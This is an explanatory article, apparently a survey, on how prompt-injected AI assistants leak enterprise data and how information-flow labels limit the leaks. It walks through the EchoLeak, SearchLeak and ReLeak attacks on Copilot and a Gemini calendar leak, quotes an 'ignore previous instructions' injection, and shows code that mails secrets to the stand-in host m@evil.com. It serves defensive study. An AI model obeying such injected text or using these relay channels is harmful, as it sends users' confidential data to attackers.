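# Containing data exfiltration by prompt-injected language model calls in enterprise systems

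## How a prompt injection makes a model call leak, and how information flow is tracked

Data exfiltration is the unauthorised transfer of data out of a system. Companies that give their staff AI assistants face a form of it that requires no stolen password or malware. Such an assistant combines a large language model, a neural network that generates text in response to text, with an ordinary program. The program fetches emails, documents and web pages, passes them to the model and carries out the actions the model requests. Some of those emails and web pages come from strangers, who can write instructions that the model follows as if the user had typed them, such as a request for the user's confidential files.

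Security researchers call this attack prompt injection. Simon Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, recalls coining the term by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which the contents of a web form end up inside a database command. In both attacks, a program joins trusted and untrusted text into one string, and no later step can reliably separate the two. Jailbreaking differs from prompt injection in that the user attacks the model instead of being the victim.

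Vendors train their models to resist injected instructions, and some sell filters that detect them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, conjectures that persistent attackers will always get past these defences. If that is right, it makes sense to assume that an injection will succeed and to limit the data it can leak.

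### From the attacker's email to the leak

A model call is one request to a language model, which takes the whole prompt as input and returns either text or a request for an action. A tool call is an action that the model requests and the surrounding program carries out, such as sending an email or opening a web address. An agent is a loop in which the program calls the model, runs any tool the model requests, appends the result to the conversation and calls the model again with the whole conversation, until the model produces a final answer.

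*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, Microsoft, 2025) gives an example. An employee asks the assistant to summarise recent emails on Project X and send the summary to the employee's manager. One of the emails comes from an attacker and tells the reader to ignore previous instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to an outside address. The model first requests the emails, as the task requires. The program fetches them and adds them to the conversation, which now contains both the employee's request and the attacker's instructions. On the next call, the model may respond with a request to send the top email to the attacker, and the program then sends it.

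Each step in this sequence was legitimate on its own. The employee may read the mailbox, and the assistant may send mail for the employee, so access control, the usual way of protecting files, does not help much here. *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) explains that access control and encryption do not directly enforce policies about where information flows.

Costa and colleagues assume that the attacker can tamper with the data that tools fetch from untrusted sources and can observe the effects of certain tool calls, such as an email that arrives or a change in a website's visitor statistics. The attacker cannot see the model's prompts and responses, or alter the user's request, the developer's instructions or the tool descriptions. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* makes no assumption about how the model behaves, so its security argument applies across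 models and also covers model errors. Under either set of assumptions, the check belongs in the ordinary program, just before the program carries out the model's request.

This kind of theft requires three conditions together, which Willison calls the lethal trifecta: access to private data, exposure to untrusted text, and a way to send information out. Removing any one of them prevents the theft. But companies buy the assistant for its access to private data, and anyone who knows the employee's address can supply untrusted text, so in practice most of the effort goes into blocking the ways to send information out. Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers had demonstrated the flaw by June 2025 (EchoLeak, against Microsoft 365 Copilot, is the best known in enterprise software), and notes that vendors usually fixed it by blocking the channel the researchers had used to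 send data out.

It is hard to identify every way data can leave a system, though. If the assistant can display an image from a web address, an attacker can have stolen text encoded in the address, and displaying the image sends the text to the attacker. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes a less obvious case with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant. Claude Code asked for human approval before running many of the shell commands that can send data to unknown domains, but it allowed `ping`, which tests whether a machine responds, without approval. An attacker's instruction, hidden in a code file, made the assistant read secret keys and ping an address that contained them. Looking up that address sent the keys to the attacker's server.

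### Sources, sinks and labels

An assistant that can never send an email is of limited use, so some outbound channels have to stay open. Information-flow control (IFC) is a way to decide which data may leave through them. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, an article on the company's prototypes, reduces it to labelling data, propagating the labels and checking them before acting. Labels are applied at the sources, where data enters the system, and checked at the sinks, where data can leave or take effect. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) counts as a source any tool whose results may contain attacker-controlled content, such as web search or email. A mailbox is a source of both the attacker's text and the secrets the attacker wants.

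Information-flow tracking therefore uses two kinds of label. A confidentiality label records who may read a piece of data, and an integrity label records whether the data is trusted or could have come from an attacker. The theory of combining labels goes back to *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976). Denning's model has a set of security classes, a relation that specifies which class may flow into which, and an operator that gives the class of any result computed from two inputs. Denning showed that under mild assumptions these form a lattice, so any two classes have a least upper bound, or join, which is the least restrictive class into which both may flow. The class of a result has to be the join of the classes of its inputs. In particular, a result must be at least as restricted as each input, because a program that could store `a + b` where it may not store `a`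 could set `b` to zero and store `a` there anyway.

For an office, the most useful confidentiality labels are sets of readers. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one document and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, then only Bob and Carol may read a text that draws on both. The join is the intersection of the sets, and a smaller set is a stricter label. For integrity, the values "trusted" and "untrusted" usually suffice, and one untrusted input makes the result untrusted. Most systems carry the two labels as a pair.

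Microsoft's worked example has no attacker in it. Alex asks an assistant to handle the unanswered emails in an inbox. Priya has sent a preview of the quarterly sales. Marco has also written, is curious about the figures, and has no right to see them yet. Priya's email carries the label {Alex, Priya} and Marco's carries {Alex, Marco}. Once the assistant has read both, anything it writes has the label

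{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

Before a reply goes out, the program compares its recipients with this set. Marco is not in it, so no reply to Marco leaves without Alex's review, whatever the reply happens to contain. Had Priya copied Marco in on the sales email, the intersection would have been {Alex, Marco} and the reply could have gone out unattended. (A reply to Priya needs review too, since Marco's email may hold things that Priya should not see.)

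The same comparison stops the theft from the Project X mailbox. The attacker is allowed to read only the email they wrote, so their outside address drops out of the intersection as soon as the assistant reads anyone else's mail. The manager may also drop out if they did not receive every email the assistant read. The check then holds up a message that the employee asked the assistant to send to the manager.

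### Noninterference, and two ways for data to flow

What would it mean for a system to leak nothing at all? Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, gave the standard answer, noninterference. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing that the first group does affects what the second group sees. Formally, take any sequence of commands *w* and any user *u* in the second group, and delete from *w* every command that the first group issued. Then *u* must see the same output either way:

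out(*w*, *u*) = out(*w* without the first group's commands, *u*).

For secret data, the condition is that changing the secret changes nothing an outsider can observe. For example, two mailboxes that differ only in the text of one confidential email must look identical from outside. Because language models' responses are partly random, *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) restates the condition in terms of probabilities and gives machine-checked proofs that it holds for a small programming language for agents. This version still allows an observer to learn from whether a program finishes.

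Data can violate noninterference in two ways. An explicit flow copies the secret, or something computed from it, into the output:

```
text = read_email(top)
send_email("m@evil.com", text)
```

An implicit flow lets the secret determine what happens, without any of it appearing in the output. Garby and colleagues give this example:

```
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
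```

The word "rich!" is a constant and no secret, but its arrival reveals something about the balance, and so does its failure to arrive. A monitor can deal with the email by giving everything inside the `if` the label of the condition. The case where the branch does not run is harder. Denning discusses a short program, due to the computer scientist J. S. Fenton, in which `a` is secret:

```
b = c = false
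if not a: c = true
if not c: b = true
```

If `a` is true, the program skips the second line, `c` stays false with its public label, and the third line makes `b` true. If `a` is false, `c` becomes true with a secret label, the program skips the third line, and `b` stays false. Either way, `b` ends up equal to `a` but keeps its public label, because a monitor that tracks only the lines that run cannot relabel a variable in a skipped line. Garby and colleagues show that CaMeL, a recent agent design from Google DeepMind, has the same gap. Denning's remedy was to have a compiler examine both branches beforehand and insert the missing label updates, which requires access to the program text.

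Full noninterference is too restrictive for most working systems. Costa and colleagues judge that it would essentially bar an agent from calling any tool with publicly visible effects after any call that may have read a secret. They settle for explicit secrecy, a weaker property that rules out explicit flows but allows some implicit ones. An observer who can see the sequence of tool calls may still infer a little from the agent's choices. This tradeoff seems reasonable against an attacker who wants whole documents, but less so when the secret is a single yes or no.

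Even the weaker property needs exceptions, as the manager's summary shows. Askarov and Myers (2011), in *Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity*, describe the two standard ones. Declassification relaxes a confidentiality label, as when the employee confirms that the manager may have the summary. Endorsement relaxes an integrity label, as when a program treats an untrusted value as trusted after checking that it is one of a few permitted values. Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, warn that declassification can cause unintended releases. An injected instruction that could trigger a declassification would defeat the scheme, so Microsoft's prototype policy for posting in a Teams channel lets a message go out without the user's approval only if the context is trusted or every member of the channel may already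 read the content.

### Why a model call defeats the tracking

Denning's compiler could work out the label of `a + b*c` by reading the expression. But Xu, Li and colleagues (2026) write in *Sightline* that no code describes what happens inside a model call, because the model transforms the prompt in its weights. The model's architecture also does little to narrow down which parts of the prompt could have affected the output. In a transformer, the design behind most current language models, an operation called attention moves information between positions in the text. Attention draws on every earlier part of the prompt at least a little, and Xu and colleagues prove that a part it draws on only faintly can still determine the output.

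Comparing a model's output with its inputs does not settle whether the output leaks information from them. A model can paraphrase, translate or encode a confidential email so that no phrase of the original survives. Like the two-line balance program, it can also leak information through a choice, as when one sentence in the prompt determines the recipient or a yes or no answer. *Ghost in the Agent* therefore applies the distinction between explicit and implicit flows to model outputs. A model can produce both in a single step, with no `if` statement to identify the implicit flow.

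So careful systems fall back on a conservative rule: the output of a model call takes the join of the labels of everything in its prompt. With labels ℓ₁ to ℓₙ on the inputs,

label(output) = ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ,

where ⊔ stands for the join. The rule is safe, and the proof is short. Suppose the output in fact drew on only a few of the inputs. Its correct label is the join of those few. Adding the remaining inputs can only make the join stricter, because intersecting one more set of readers removes names and never adds any. Any recipient who passes the check under the strict label would also have passed under the correct one. Put concretely, if Marco passes, then Marco was entitled to read every single thing in the prompt, and it does not matter which of them the model used.

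The proof assumes that the sources are labeled correctly and that the check covers every sink. If someone has marked a salary file as public, the rule does not protect it.

### Label creep

The conservative rule spreads labels to data that does not need them. Xu and colleagues studied model calls in 2,103 families of open-source repositories and found that 12–14% of the inputs that programs inserted into prompts never reached the output. For these calls, the rule adds a needless label for roughly one in every seven or eight inputs. The rate is probably higher for an assistant that has been reading email all morning, since most of what it has read has no bearing on its next reply.

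Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, call the steady accumulation label creep. Three steps are enough to produce it in Alex's inbox:

| What enters the conversation | Label of the conversation afterwards |
|---|---|
| Marco's email, asking whether Thursday suits for a meeting | {Alex, Marco} |
| Priya's email with the sales preview | {Alex} |
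| Alex's request to tell Marco that Thursday is fine | {Alex} |

The reply to Marco does not use Priya's figures, yet it could have been sent automatically after the first row and cannot be after the second. Nothing Alex types later lifts this restriction, because a user's own messages usually count as trusted and public, and joining a public label to a strict one leaves the strict one unchanged. *APPA* (2026), which orders its labels in the opposite direction, similarly proves that over an agent's whole run, the permissions its label allows can shrink or stay the same but never grow back by themselves.

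Memory makes this worse. In Gregory and colleagues' model, agents retain what they have seen, so a strict label that an agent picks up in one task follows it into the next and passes to any other agent that receives its context. They simulated many arrangements of agents and concluded that better arrangements reduce the loss but don't prevent it. The problem predates language models. For example, Denning describes ADEPT-50, a 1960s time-sharing system in which the class of a process was the join of the classes of all the files it had opened, so it could only rise.

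### Keeping untrusted text away from the planner

One way to limit how far a conversation's labels rise is to let less into it. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed dividing the work between two models. The planner (Willison's "privileged" model) takes the user's request, chooses the actions, and never sees untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and can't call any tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, sits between them.

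Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The planner requests the email, and the controller fetches it and stores it as `$VAR1`. The planner requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller puts the real text into a prompt for the quarantined model, stores the result as `$VAR2`, and sends the planner only a notice that the summary is ready. The planner then requests that the controller display `$VAR2`. An attacker's instruction in the email can corrupt the summary, but it cannot trigger a tool call, because no model with access to tools reads it. The planner's conversation keeps its trusted label whatever the email contains.

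Willison called the proposal "pretty bad", and it has clear drawbacks. A planner that sees only variable names cannot act on the variables' contents. Costa and colleagues give the example of a request to complete the tasks due today in a to-do app, where the planner has to know what the tasks are before it can choose a tool. Willison made one exception, which lets the planner see results that the controller can verify, such as a choice from a fixed list of categories. The user is also still exposed, because a corrupted summary could contain a request to paste encoded text into a website. And the split does not determine where the contents of `$VAR2` may go. If the planner emails the summary to someone, the text still derives from private email, and only a confidentiality label can show whether the recipient should have it.

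Much of the evidence on how well such designs work comes from the *AgentDojo* (2024) benchmark, which has 97 realistic user tasks and 629 security test cases. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) describes how the benchmark plants hostile instructions in four simulated settings (an office workspace, a bank, a travel service and Slack), putting them where outside text would naturally appear, such as an email body or a file. Ordinary code then checks the state of the simulated world, for example whether an email was sent or money moved, so no model has to judge whether the attack succeeded.

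## Microsoft 365 Copilot: the EchoLeak and ReLeak disclosures

Microsoft 365 Copilot is the assistant Microsoft sells to companies as part of its office software. When an employee asks a question, Copilot first searches what that employee is allowed to read: their mailbox, Teams chats, and files in OneDrive (personal storage) and SharePoint (shared storage). It adds the best matches to the prompt along with the question. Only employees can use Copilot, but anyone can email an employee, and that email becomes part of what Copilot searches.

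One team of researchers showed in June 2025, and again in December 2026, that such an email could make Copilot leak company data. A second team found a related flaw between those dates. Microsoft patched Copilot each time, so the disclosures give some idea of how well the patches held.

### EchoLeak

Adir Gruss, a cofounder of Aim Security, told Fortune (2025) that the company's researchers spent about three months reverse-engineering Copilot. They were looking for an equivalent of the "zero-click" attacks on mobile phones, which need no action from the victim. They found one and named it EchoLeak.

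Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, gives the team's own account of the attack. The attacker emails an employee from any address. Later, the employee asks Copilot an ordinary question, and the search step retrieves the attacker's email along with genuine company material. The researchers made retrieval more likely by covering many routine workplace subjects in one long email. The model follows the instructions in the email, picks out something sensitive from the rest of its prompt and writes it into the web address of an image, which the employee's browser loads automatically.

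Anything in the prompt could leak this way, including the earlier conversation, the files and messages the search step had fetched, and details Copilot loads in advance, such as the user's and organisation's names. Aim's researchers knew of no administrator setting that would have prevented it.

One of Microsoft's defences was a classifier that screened incoming text for what Microsoft calls cross-prompt injection attacks (XPIA), meaning injections that arrive inside retrieved content. The researchers' email got past the classifier because it read like a message to a human colleague. A second defence removed links and images from Copilot's answers if they pointed outside the company. It recognised only some of the ways to write a link in Markdown, the formatting language of those answers, and the researchers used another. Copilot also normally cites the documents behind an answer, which might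 have alerted the employee, but instructions in the email could stop the model from citing it.

The last barrier was a content security policy, a web page's list of the domains from which the browser may load images. The attacker's domain was not on Copilot's list. But the list had more than two dozen entries, nearly all of them Microsoft's own services, and some of those services will fetch an outside address on a visitor's behalf. The researchers first found one in SharePoint, which worked only if the employee accepted an invitation, and then one in Teams that required no action from the employee. The browser contacted Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams contacted the attacker's server.

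EchoLeak is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public register of software flaws. The Next Web gives its severity as 9.3 out of 10 on CVSS, the standard scoring system. Willison (2025) notes that Aim reported the flaw in January 2025 and that Microsoft had rolled out a fix by 11 June. According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that the flaw had affected no customers. In a later case study, *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) call the attack the first real-world zero-click prompt injection exploit in a production system.

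Ravia proposes the name "LLM scope violation" for the central step, in which instructions from an untrusted source make the model use trusted data without the user's consent. The name is proposed by analogy with a low-privilege program that gets a high-privilege one to act for it. In terms of labels, text with an untrusted integrity label steers data with a strict confidentiality label towards an outsider. The term is more useful than "malicious email" because the email itself need not look malicious. The violation depends on the combination of the email, the rest of the prompt and the destination of the answer. Aim sells guardrails built around this idea, so it had an interest in the term catching on, but the description is useful regardless.

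### SearchLeak

Varonis Threat Labs, the research group of another security company, disclosed the next flaw a year later. The attack targeted the search function in Copilot's enterprise edition, and this time it required one click from the victim. The link led to a real microsoft.com address, so ordinary anti-phishing tools were unlikely to flag it, according to The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026). Taler (2026), in *SearchLeak*, lists login codes, email messages, meeting details and private files among the data that an attacker could steal.

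SC Media's *SearchLeak vulnerability allows data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise* summarises the three weaknesses that Varonis chained together. Text inside the link became part of the prompt, so Copilot searched the victim's data for whatever the attacker had named. While the answer was still appearing on screen, for a brief period the browser would act on an image tag before Copilot had made the text safe. The image's address pointed to Bing's image search, which the content security policy allowed, and Bing fetched the attacker's address with the stolen data in it.

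The first step of SearchLeak matters for the designs in later sections. Costa and colleagues assume that an attacker cannot alter the user's request, and most labelling schemes treat that request as trusted. In SearchLeak, the attacker wrote the request and the employee submitted it by clicking, so an integrity label would have wrongly marked it as trusted. A confidentiality label would still have worked, because the employee was allowed to read the stolen emails but the attacker's server was not, regardless of who wrote the prompt.

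The Hacker News reports that Microsoft marked SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824) critical but scored its severity at 6.5, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* attributes the difference to the user's click, which Microsoft counted as a mitigating factor, while the database assessed the flaw as needing no user interaction. Neither score is a good measure of how much data was at risk. Microsoft had fixed the flaw by the time Varonis disclosed it publicly on 15 June 2026, and customers did not have to do anything.

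### ReLeak

Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and the team behind EchoLeak became Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026 the team published *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), a report on three more zero-click attacks on Copilot, which it grouped under that name. All three begin as EchoLeak did: an employee receives an email, never opens it, and later makes a request that leads Copilot to process it. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot*, the attacks could reach corporate emails, documents, financial information and anything else the victim's permissions cover. The attacks differ in how the data gets out.

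One again used an image's address, with Bing passing the browser's request on to the attacker's server. Antipov (2026), in the Russian news report *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* ("You don't even have to open the email"), notes that SearchLeak had used a similar channel but needed a click. The team reported its three flaws to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August 2026, after the June fix for SearchLeak. This suggests that the fix closed one path to Bing but left Bing usable as a relay.

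The second attack used Copilot's ability to create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them to OneDrive or SharePoint. The researchers got Copilot to save a file containing a link with confidential data in the address. Microsoft's servers visited the link while processing the stored file in the background. Antipov reports that in the team's tests this happened between one and eight minutes after the conversation had ended, even if the employee never opened the file. A monitor that watched only the conversation would have recorded a new document in the employee's own folder and no outgoing traffic.

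The third went through Copilot's code interpreter, which runs Python programs in a sandbox that is supposed to be isolated. According to Microsoft's documentation, these sandboxes have no incoming or outgoing network traffic. The researchers found a way around the restriction, and their code sent the data to an outside server without a relay. Agents that customers build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio can also use the code interpreter, but according to Antipov, nobody has confirmed that the flaw extended to them.

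The routes worked independently. An attacker could in principle have combined them, but the team did not demonstrate all three together.

| Flaw | Way in | What contacted the attacker's server | CVSS score | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak, CVE-2025-32711 | Email | A Teams service that fetches links | 9.3 | By 11 June 2025 |
| SearchLeak, CVE-2026-42824 | One click on a link | Bing image search | 6.5 or 7.5 | By 15 June 2026 |
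| ReLeak, CVE-2026-78501 | Email | Python code in the sandbox | 8.6 | 17 September 2026 |
| ReLeak, CVE-2026-124132 | Email | Background processing of stored files | Not public | 11 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, CVE-2026-124115 | Email | Bing | Not public | 15 November 2026 |

The sandbox flaw first had a score of 7.4, which Microsoft later raised. When Cato published, the other two identifiers were still marked "reserved", meaning their full public records did not exist yet. Microsoft took four to seven weeks to fix the sandbox flaw and about 12 to 16 weeks to fix each of the other two. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, reports that Microsoft made the repairs on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Customers also could not fix the product themselves in the meantime.

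### Why the injection filter did not hold

Microsoft's classifier was running during both EchoLeak and ReLeak, and failed both times. Ravia attributes the 2025 failure to the malicious email's wording, which addressed the instructions to the recipient and never mentioned an AI, an assistant or Copilot. Punto Informatico's *ReLeak* gives much the same reason for 2026, reporting that Copilot would not carry out blatant commands but could be deceived by instructions that resembled legitimate requests.

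This is hard to fix with a better classifier. Office email consists largely of people telling other people what to do, often with confidential material. "Put last quarter's figures in the attached form" could be a normal request from a manager or an attack from a stranger. A classifier cannot tell which from the text alone, because the difference lies in who sent it and where the form goes. Ravia adds that good collections of real injections to train on are scarce, while the possible topics, tones and languages are nearly unlimited. A stricter filter would catch more attacks but would also withhold legitimate email like the manager's.

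The attacker can also keep trying. Suppose a filter stops 99 of every 100 differently worded attempts, and suppose for simplicity that the attempts are independent. The chance that at least one of 100 versions gets through is then

1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 0.63.

A real attacker learns from each failure. For ReLeak, Cato's team had AI agents do this. According to Antipov, the agents, directed by human specialists, wrote test cases, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next round.

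The research literature points the same way. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injections, using attacks tuned to each defence through methods including automated search, reinforcement learning and human effort. Most of the defences had originally reported attack success rates near zero, but most failed more than 90% of the time against the tuned attacks. The original evaluations had mainly replayed known attacks, so they did not show how well the defences would handle new ones. Laboratory attackers get many more tries and much better feedback than someone emailing a stranger's company, so these results may overstate the risk from careless attackers. But companies can buy Copilot, so a careful attacker could rehearse on their own account before sending anything to the target. The ReLeak team succeeded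 against a commercial product whose internals Microsoft does not publish.

The classifier is still useful because it stops crude attempts and makes the rest harder. But a company cannot rely on it to keep a specific file from leaving.

### Microsoft's layers

A few weeks after EchoLeak became public, Microsoft's Security Response Center published *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* (2025). The post describes defence in depth, with several layers so that the failure of one does not necessarily let an attack succeed. The first layer is meant to prevent the model from obeying injected text. It uses carefully written developer instructions and Spotlighting, which marks or transforms untrusted text so that the model can tell it from instructions. The next layer detects attacks with Prompt Shields, a classifier of the kind described above. The last limits the damage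 when an injection succeeds by restricting which data the assistant can reach, asking the user to consent to certain actions, and blocking known ways of getting data out.

The post distinguishes probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to work, from deterministic ones, which rule out an outcome by construction. Spotlighting and Prompt Shields are probabilistic. The removal of outside links, the image policy and the sandbox's network isolation are deterministic, and should still have worked after the classifier failed.

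The deterministic layers failed too, for more ordinary reasons. The link filter missed a notation, the policy allowed services that forward requests, and the sandbox had a hole. The Next Web notes that security teams have dealt with bugs like SearchLeak's for years, and that prompt injection makes these old web flaws dangerous again. This is somewhat encouraging, because engineers can find and close a hole in a sandbox, whereas nobody knows how to make a classifier recognise every deceptive email. However, a deterministic layer blocks only the exfiltration routes its designers thought of.

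### Which services count as sinks

The image policy is the clearest example. It listed the servers that the browser could contact, and in EchoLeak it enforced that list correctly. But a company needs to know where the data finally arrives. If a single permitted service forwards requests to any address it is given, the list in effect permits the whole internet. An allow-listed service that relays data outward is therefore a sink, and a label check has to treat a request to it as a message to an unknown reader.

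The list that Ravia published in 2025 already included bing.com, the domain that relayed data in both SearchLeak and ReLeak a year later. Aim's researchers had used Teams in EchoLeak, which Microsoft fixed. A review of every listed service for the ability to fetch outside addresses might have found the problem with bing.com, but it would have been a large job covering more than one list. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, an independent researcher's account of other Copilot flaws, found that the policy varies between the programs in which Copilot appears and is often too permissive, and concluded that it is not a reliable security boundary there.

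New features also add sinks. EchoLeak relied on an image in a chat answer, but by 2026 Copilot could also write files and run code, and each ability gave data another way to leave. Willison (2026) describes another case from May of that year in Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft product whose agents could send email to the user's own inbox without approval. These emails could leak data even though they went to the user, because they could contain outside images that loaded when the user opened them. OneDrive can create download links that require no login, so an injection could expose a file by leaking its link.

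A simple label check can miss leaks through the inbox and stored documents. An answer labelled {Alex} passes the check when it is saved to Alex's folder or mailed to Alex, because Alex is a permitted reader. The leak occurs after the assistant's check, when the mail program or file processor contacts an address inside the text. Either the label has to stay on the file, so that every later process that opens it checks again, or the assistant has to treat saving any text with an outside link as sending that text outside. The second rule is cruder but does not require every other Microsoft service to check labels. Microsoft's research design, FIDES, puts labels and checks around each tool call, and its protection likewise depends on what the designers count as a sink. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT instead restricts what the assistant can reach, which leaves fewer exits to check.

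All of these attacks were demonstrations by researchers, and Microsoft has since patched all the flaws. Cato said in December that it knew of no affected customers, as Aim had said of EchoLeak. The demonstrations prove that a path for stealing data existed, but not how often an attack would succeed against an ordinary company or whether criminals had found the same path.

The lack of known victims is also weaker evidence that no data was stolen than it would be for most break-ins. In the relay attacks, the employee's computer contacted only Microsoft, and a Microsoft server contacted the attacker. In the file attack, the employee's computer was not involved in sending the data. A company that searched its own network records for traffic to a suspicious domain would probably have found nothing, so evidence of any real theft would be mainly in Microsoft's logs.

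## ChatGPT Lockdown Mode and Copilot Tuning: restricting what a call can reach

Microsoft closed each route for leaking data from Copilot after researchers had found it. A vendor can also act in advance by disabling features that might send data out, as OpenAI does in ChatGPT with an optional setting called Lockdown Mode. Or it can let a model use a text only if everyone who will see the model's answers may already read it. Microsoft applies this rule to training data in Copilot Tuning, a service that adapts a model to a company's own documents. Both measures are blunt, but neither depends on knowing which inputs the model used to produce an output.

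### What Lockdown Mode switches off

OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode in February 2026 for its enterprise, education and healthcare plans. In June it extended the setting to personal accounts and to business accounts that customers set up themselves. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), the intended users are people such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and most users do not need it. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the help page for the setting, lists these restrictions:

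| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Stored copies of pages only; search results may be old or missing |
| Images in answers | ChatGPT may not display them or fetch them from the web |
| Deep research, which compiles long reports from many sources | Off |
| Agent mode, which carries out tasks on websites | Off |
| Canvas, a workspace for text and code | Users cannot let generated code access the network |
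| File downloads | ChatGPT cannot fetch files to analyse |

Users can still upload files and images themselves, and image generation still works. The restriction on images targets the channel that EchoLeak used.

The limit on browsing closes a similar channel. Opening a web page sends the page's address to the site, just as loading an image does, so an address that contains a secret reveals the secret to whoever runs the site.

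OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes ChatGPT's ordinary protection against this. ChatGPT opens an address automatically only if that exact address is already in an index of public addresses. A crawler with no access to users' conversations builds the index. An address the model has just made up from someone's private data will almost certainly not be there, so ChatGPT tries another site or warns the user. OpenAI preferred this to a list of trusted domains because trusted sites often redirect visitors elsewhere.

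At least in principle, an attacker could still extract data despite the index. They could publish one page for each letter of the alphabet, wait for the crawler to record them, and have the model open them in the order that spells a password. Each address would be public and harmless by itself, but the order of the visits in the attacker's log would reveal the password. OpenAI's stated guarantee covers only data in the address.

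In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT reads copies of web pages that OpenAI has already stored. No live request leaves OpenAI's network, so the attacker's server has nothing to record, regardless of which pages the model chooses or in what order. This also rules out relays like the Bing service in the Copilot attacks, because no outside service receives a request it could forward.

The stored page can still contain an injection, and the model may still follow it, so the user might get a wrong or manipulated answer. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, approves of the design because ordinary software enforces the limits, rather than an AI system that an attacker could fool. He also infers that ChatGPT in its default settings lacks robust protection against a determined attacker. That seems right, since OpenAI says it turned some features off entirely because it could not give strong guarantees for them.

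### What stays open

Lockdown Mode does not change memory, file uploads or the ability to share a conversation. Personal users can switch it off for a single chat, and something ChatGPT remembered from a restricted chat might then be available in an unrestricted one. Lockdown Mode also does not affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant, which has its own controls for the sites it may contact.

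The largest opening is apps, the connections through which ChatGPT reads and changes data in other services. On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks live access to outside services and write actions where they conflict with its protections. When the June version launched, connectors that used data already copied to OpenAI still worked, according to Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks*. In company-managed workspaces, Lockdown Mode does not automatically disable every app. Administrators choose which apps and actions each group may use. So the default can be looser for a large company than for an individual, although the company probably has more to lose.

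To help administrators choose, OpenAI rates the actions by how easily they could leak data:

| Action | Risk |
|---|---|
| Reading or writing in an untrusted app | High |
| Writing in a trusted app, where the result has a broad or uncertain audience | High |
| Writing in a trusted app, where only trusted people can see the result | Medium |
| Reading in a trusted app | Medium, but lower than writing |
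| Searching an index that administrators manage | Medium |

Reading from an untrusted app has as high a risk rating as writing to it, which makes sense because a read request also sends data. The search terms go to the app's operator, and an injected instruction could put a secret in them. Reading from a trusted app is risky mainly because it brings confidential material into the conversation, and an attacker may then get that material out some other way.

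No action on the list is rated low. OpenAI says that Lockdown Mode should substantially reduce the risk but does not guarantee that data cannot leave, since apps, unforeseen combinations of features and new techniques may still let it out.

### A leak through a calendar

The second row of the ranking covers a flaw in Gemini, Google's AI assistant, that the security company Miggo disclosed in January 2026. Gemini reads a user's calendar to answer questions about it. The attacker sent the target a meeting invitation with instructions in the description, which took effect only when the target asked Gemini a routine question, such as whether they had any meetings on Tuesday. Gemini then read the invitation along with the rest of the calendar, summarised the target's meetings for a particular day, including private ones, and wrote the summary into the description of a new event. According to CX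 Today's *A Google Calendar Invite, a Hidden Prompt*, Gemini told the target only "It's a free time slot."

The Hacker News reports that in many companies' calendar configurations, the attacker could see the new event and read the summary in it. Google confirmed and fixed the flaw, according to SecurityWeek's *Weaponized Invite Enabled Calendar Data Theft via Google Gemini*. Miggo pointed out that the instructions could plausibly have come from the user, the same difficulty that caused Microsoft's classifier to fail.

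The data went from one part of Google Calendar to another without the model opening a web address or loading an image, so a control on web traffic would have had nothing to block. Praetorian, another security company that The Hacker News quotes, says that any field, log, database entry or file a model can write to is a potential route for exfiltrating data.

An equivalent attack on a personal ChatGPT account in Lockdown Mode should fail, because Lockdown Mode blocks the kind of write action the attack needs. In a managed workspace, the result would depend on whether an administrator had allowed ChatGPT to create events. To make that decision well, the administrator would have to know who can see new events by default, which someone may have set years earlier for convenience. A check on reader labels would depend on the same information, because it can stop the write only if the program counts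 everyone who can view the event as a recipient.

### Content that every participant may read

Closing exits does not help if the attacker is the person the user means to write to. Bhatt, Rajore and colleagues (2025), in *Position*, work through a case of this kind. The paper comes from Microsoft researchers, and the attack goes as follows:

1. Bob emails Alice to suggest a meeting. Hidden text, perhaps white letters on a white background, asks the reader to look up Project X's revenue in millions and propose that day of the month.
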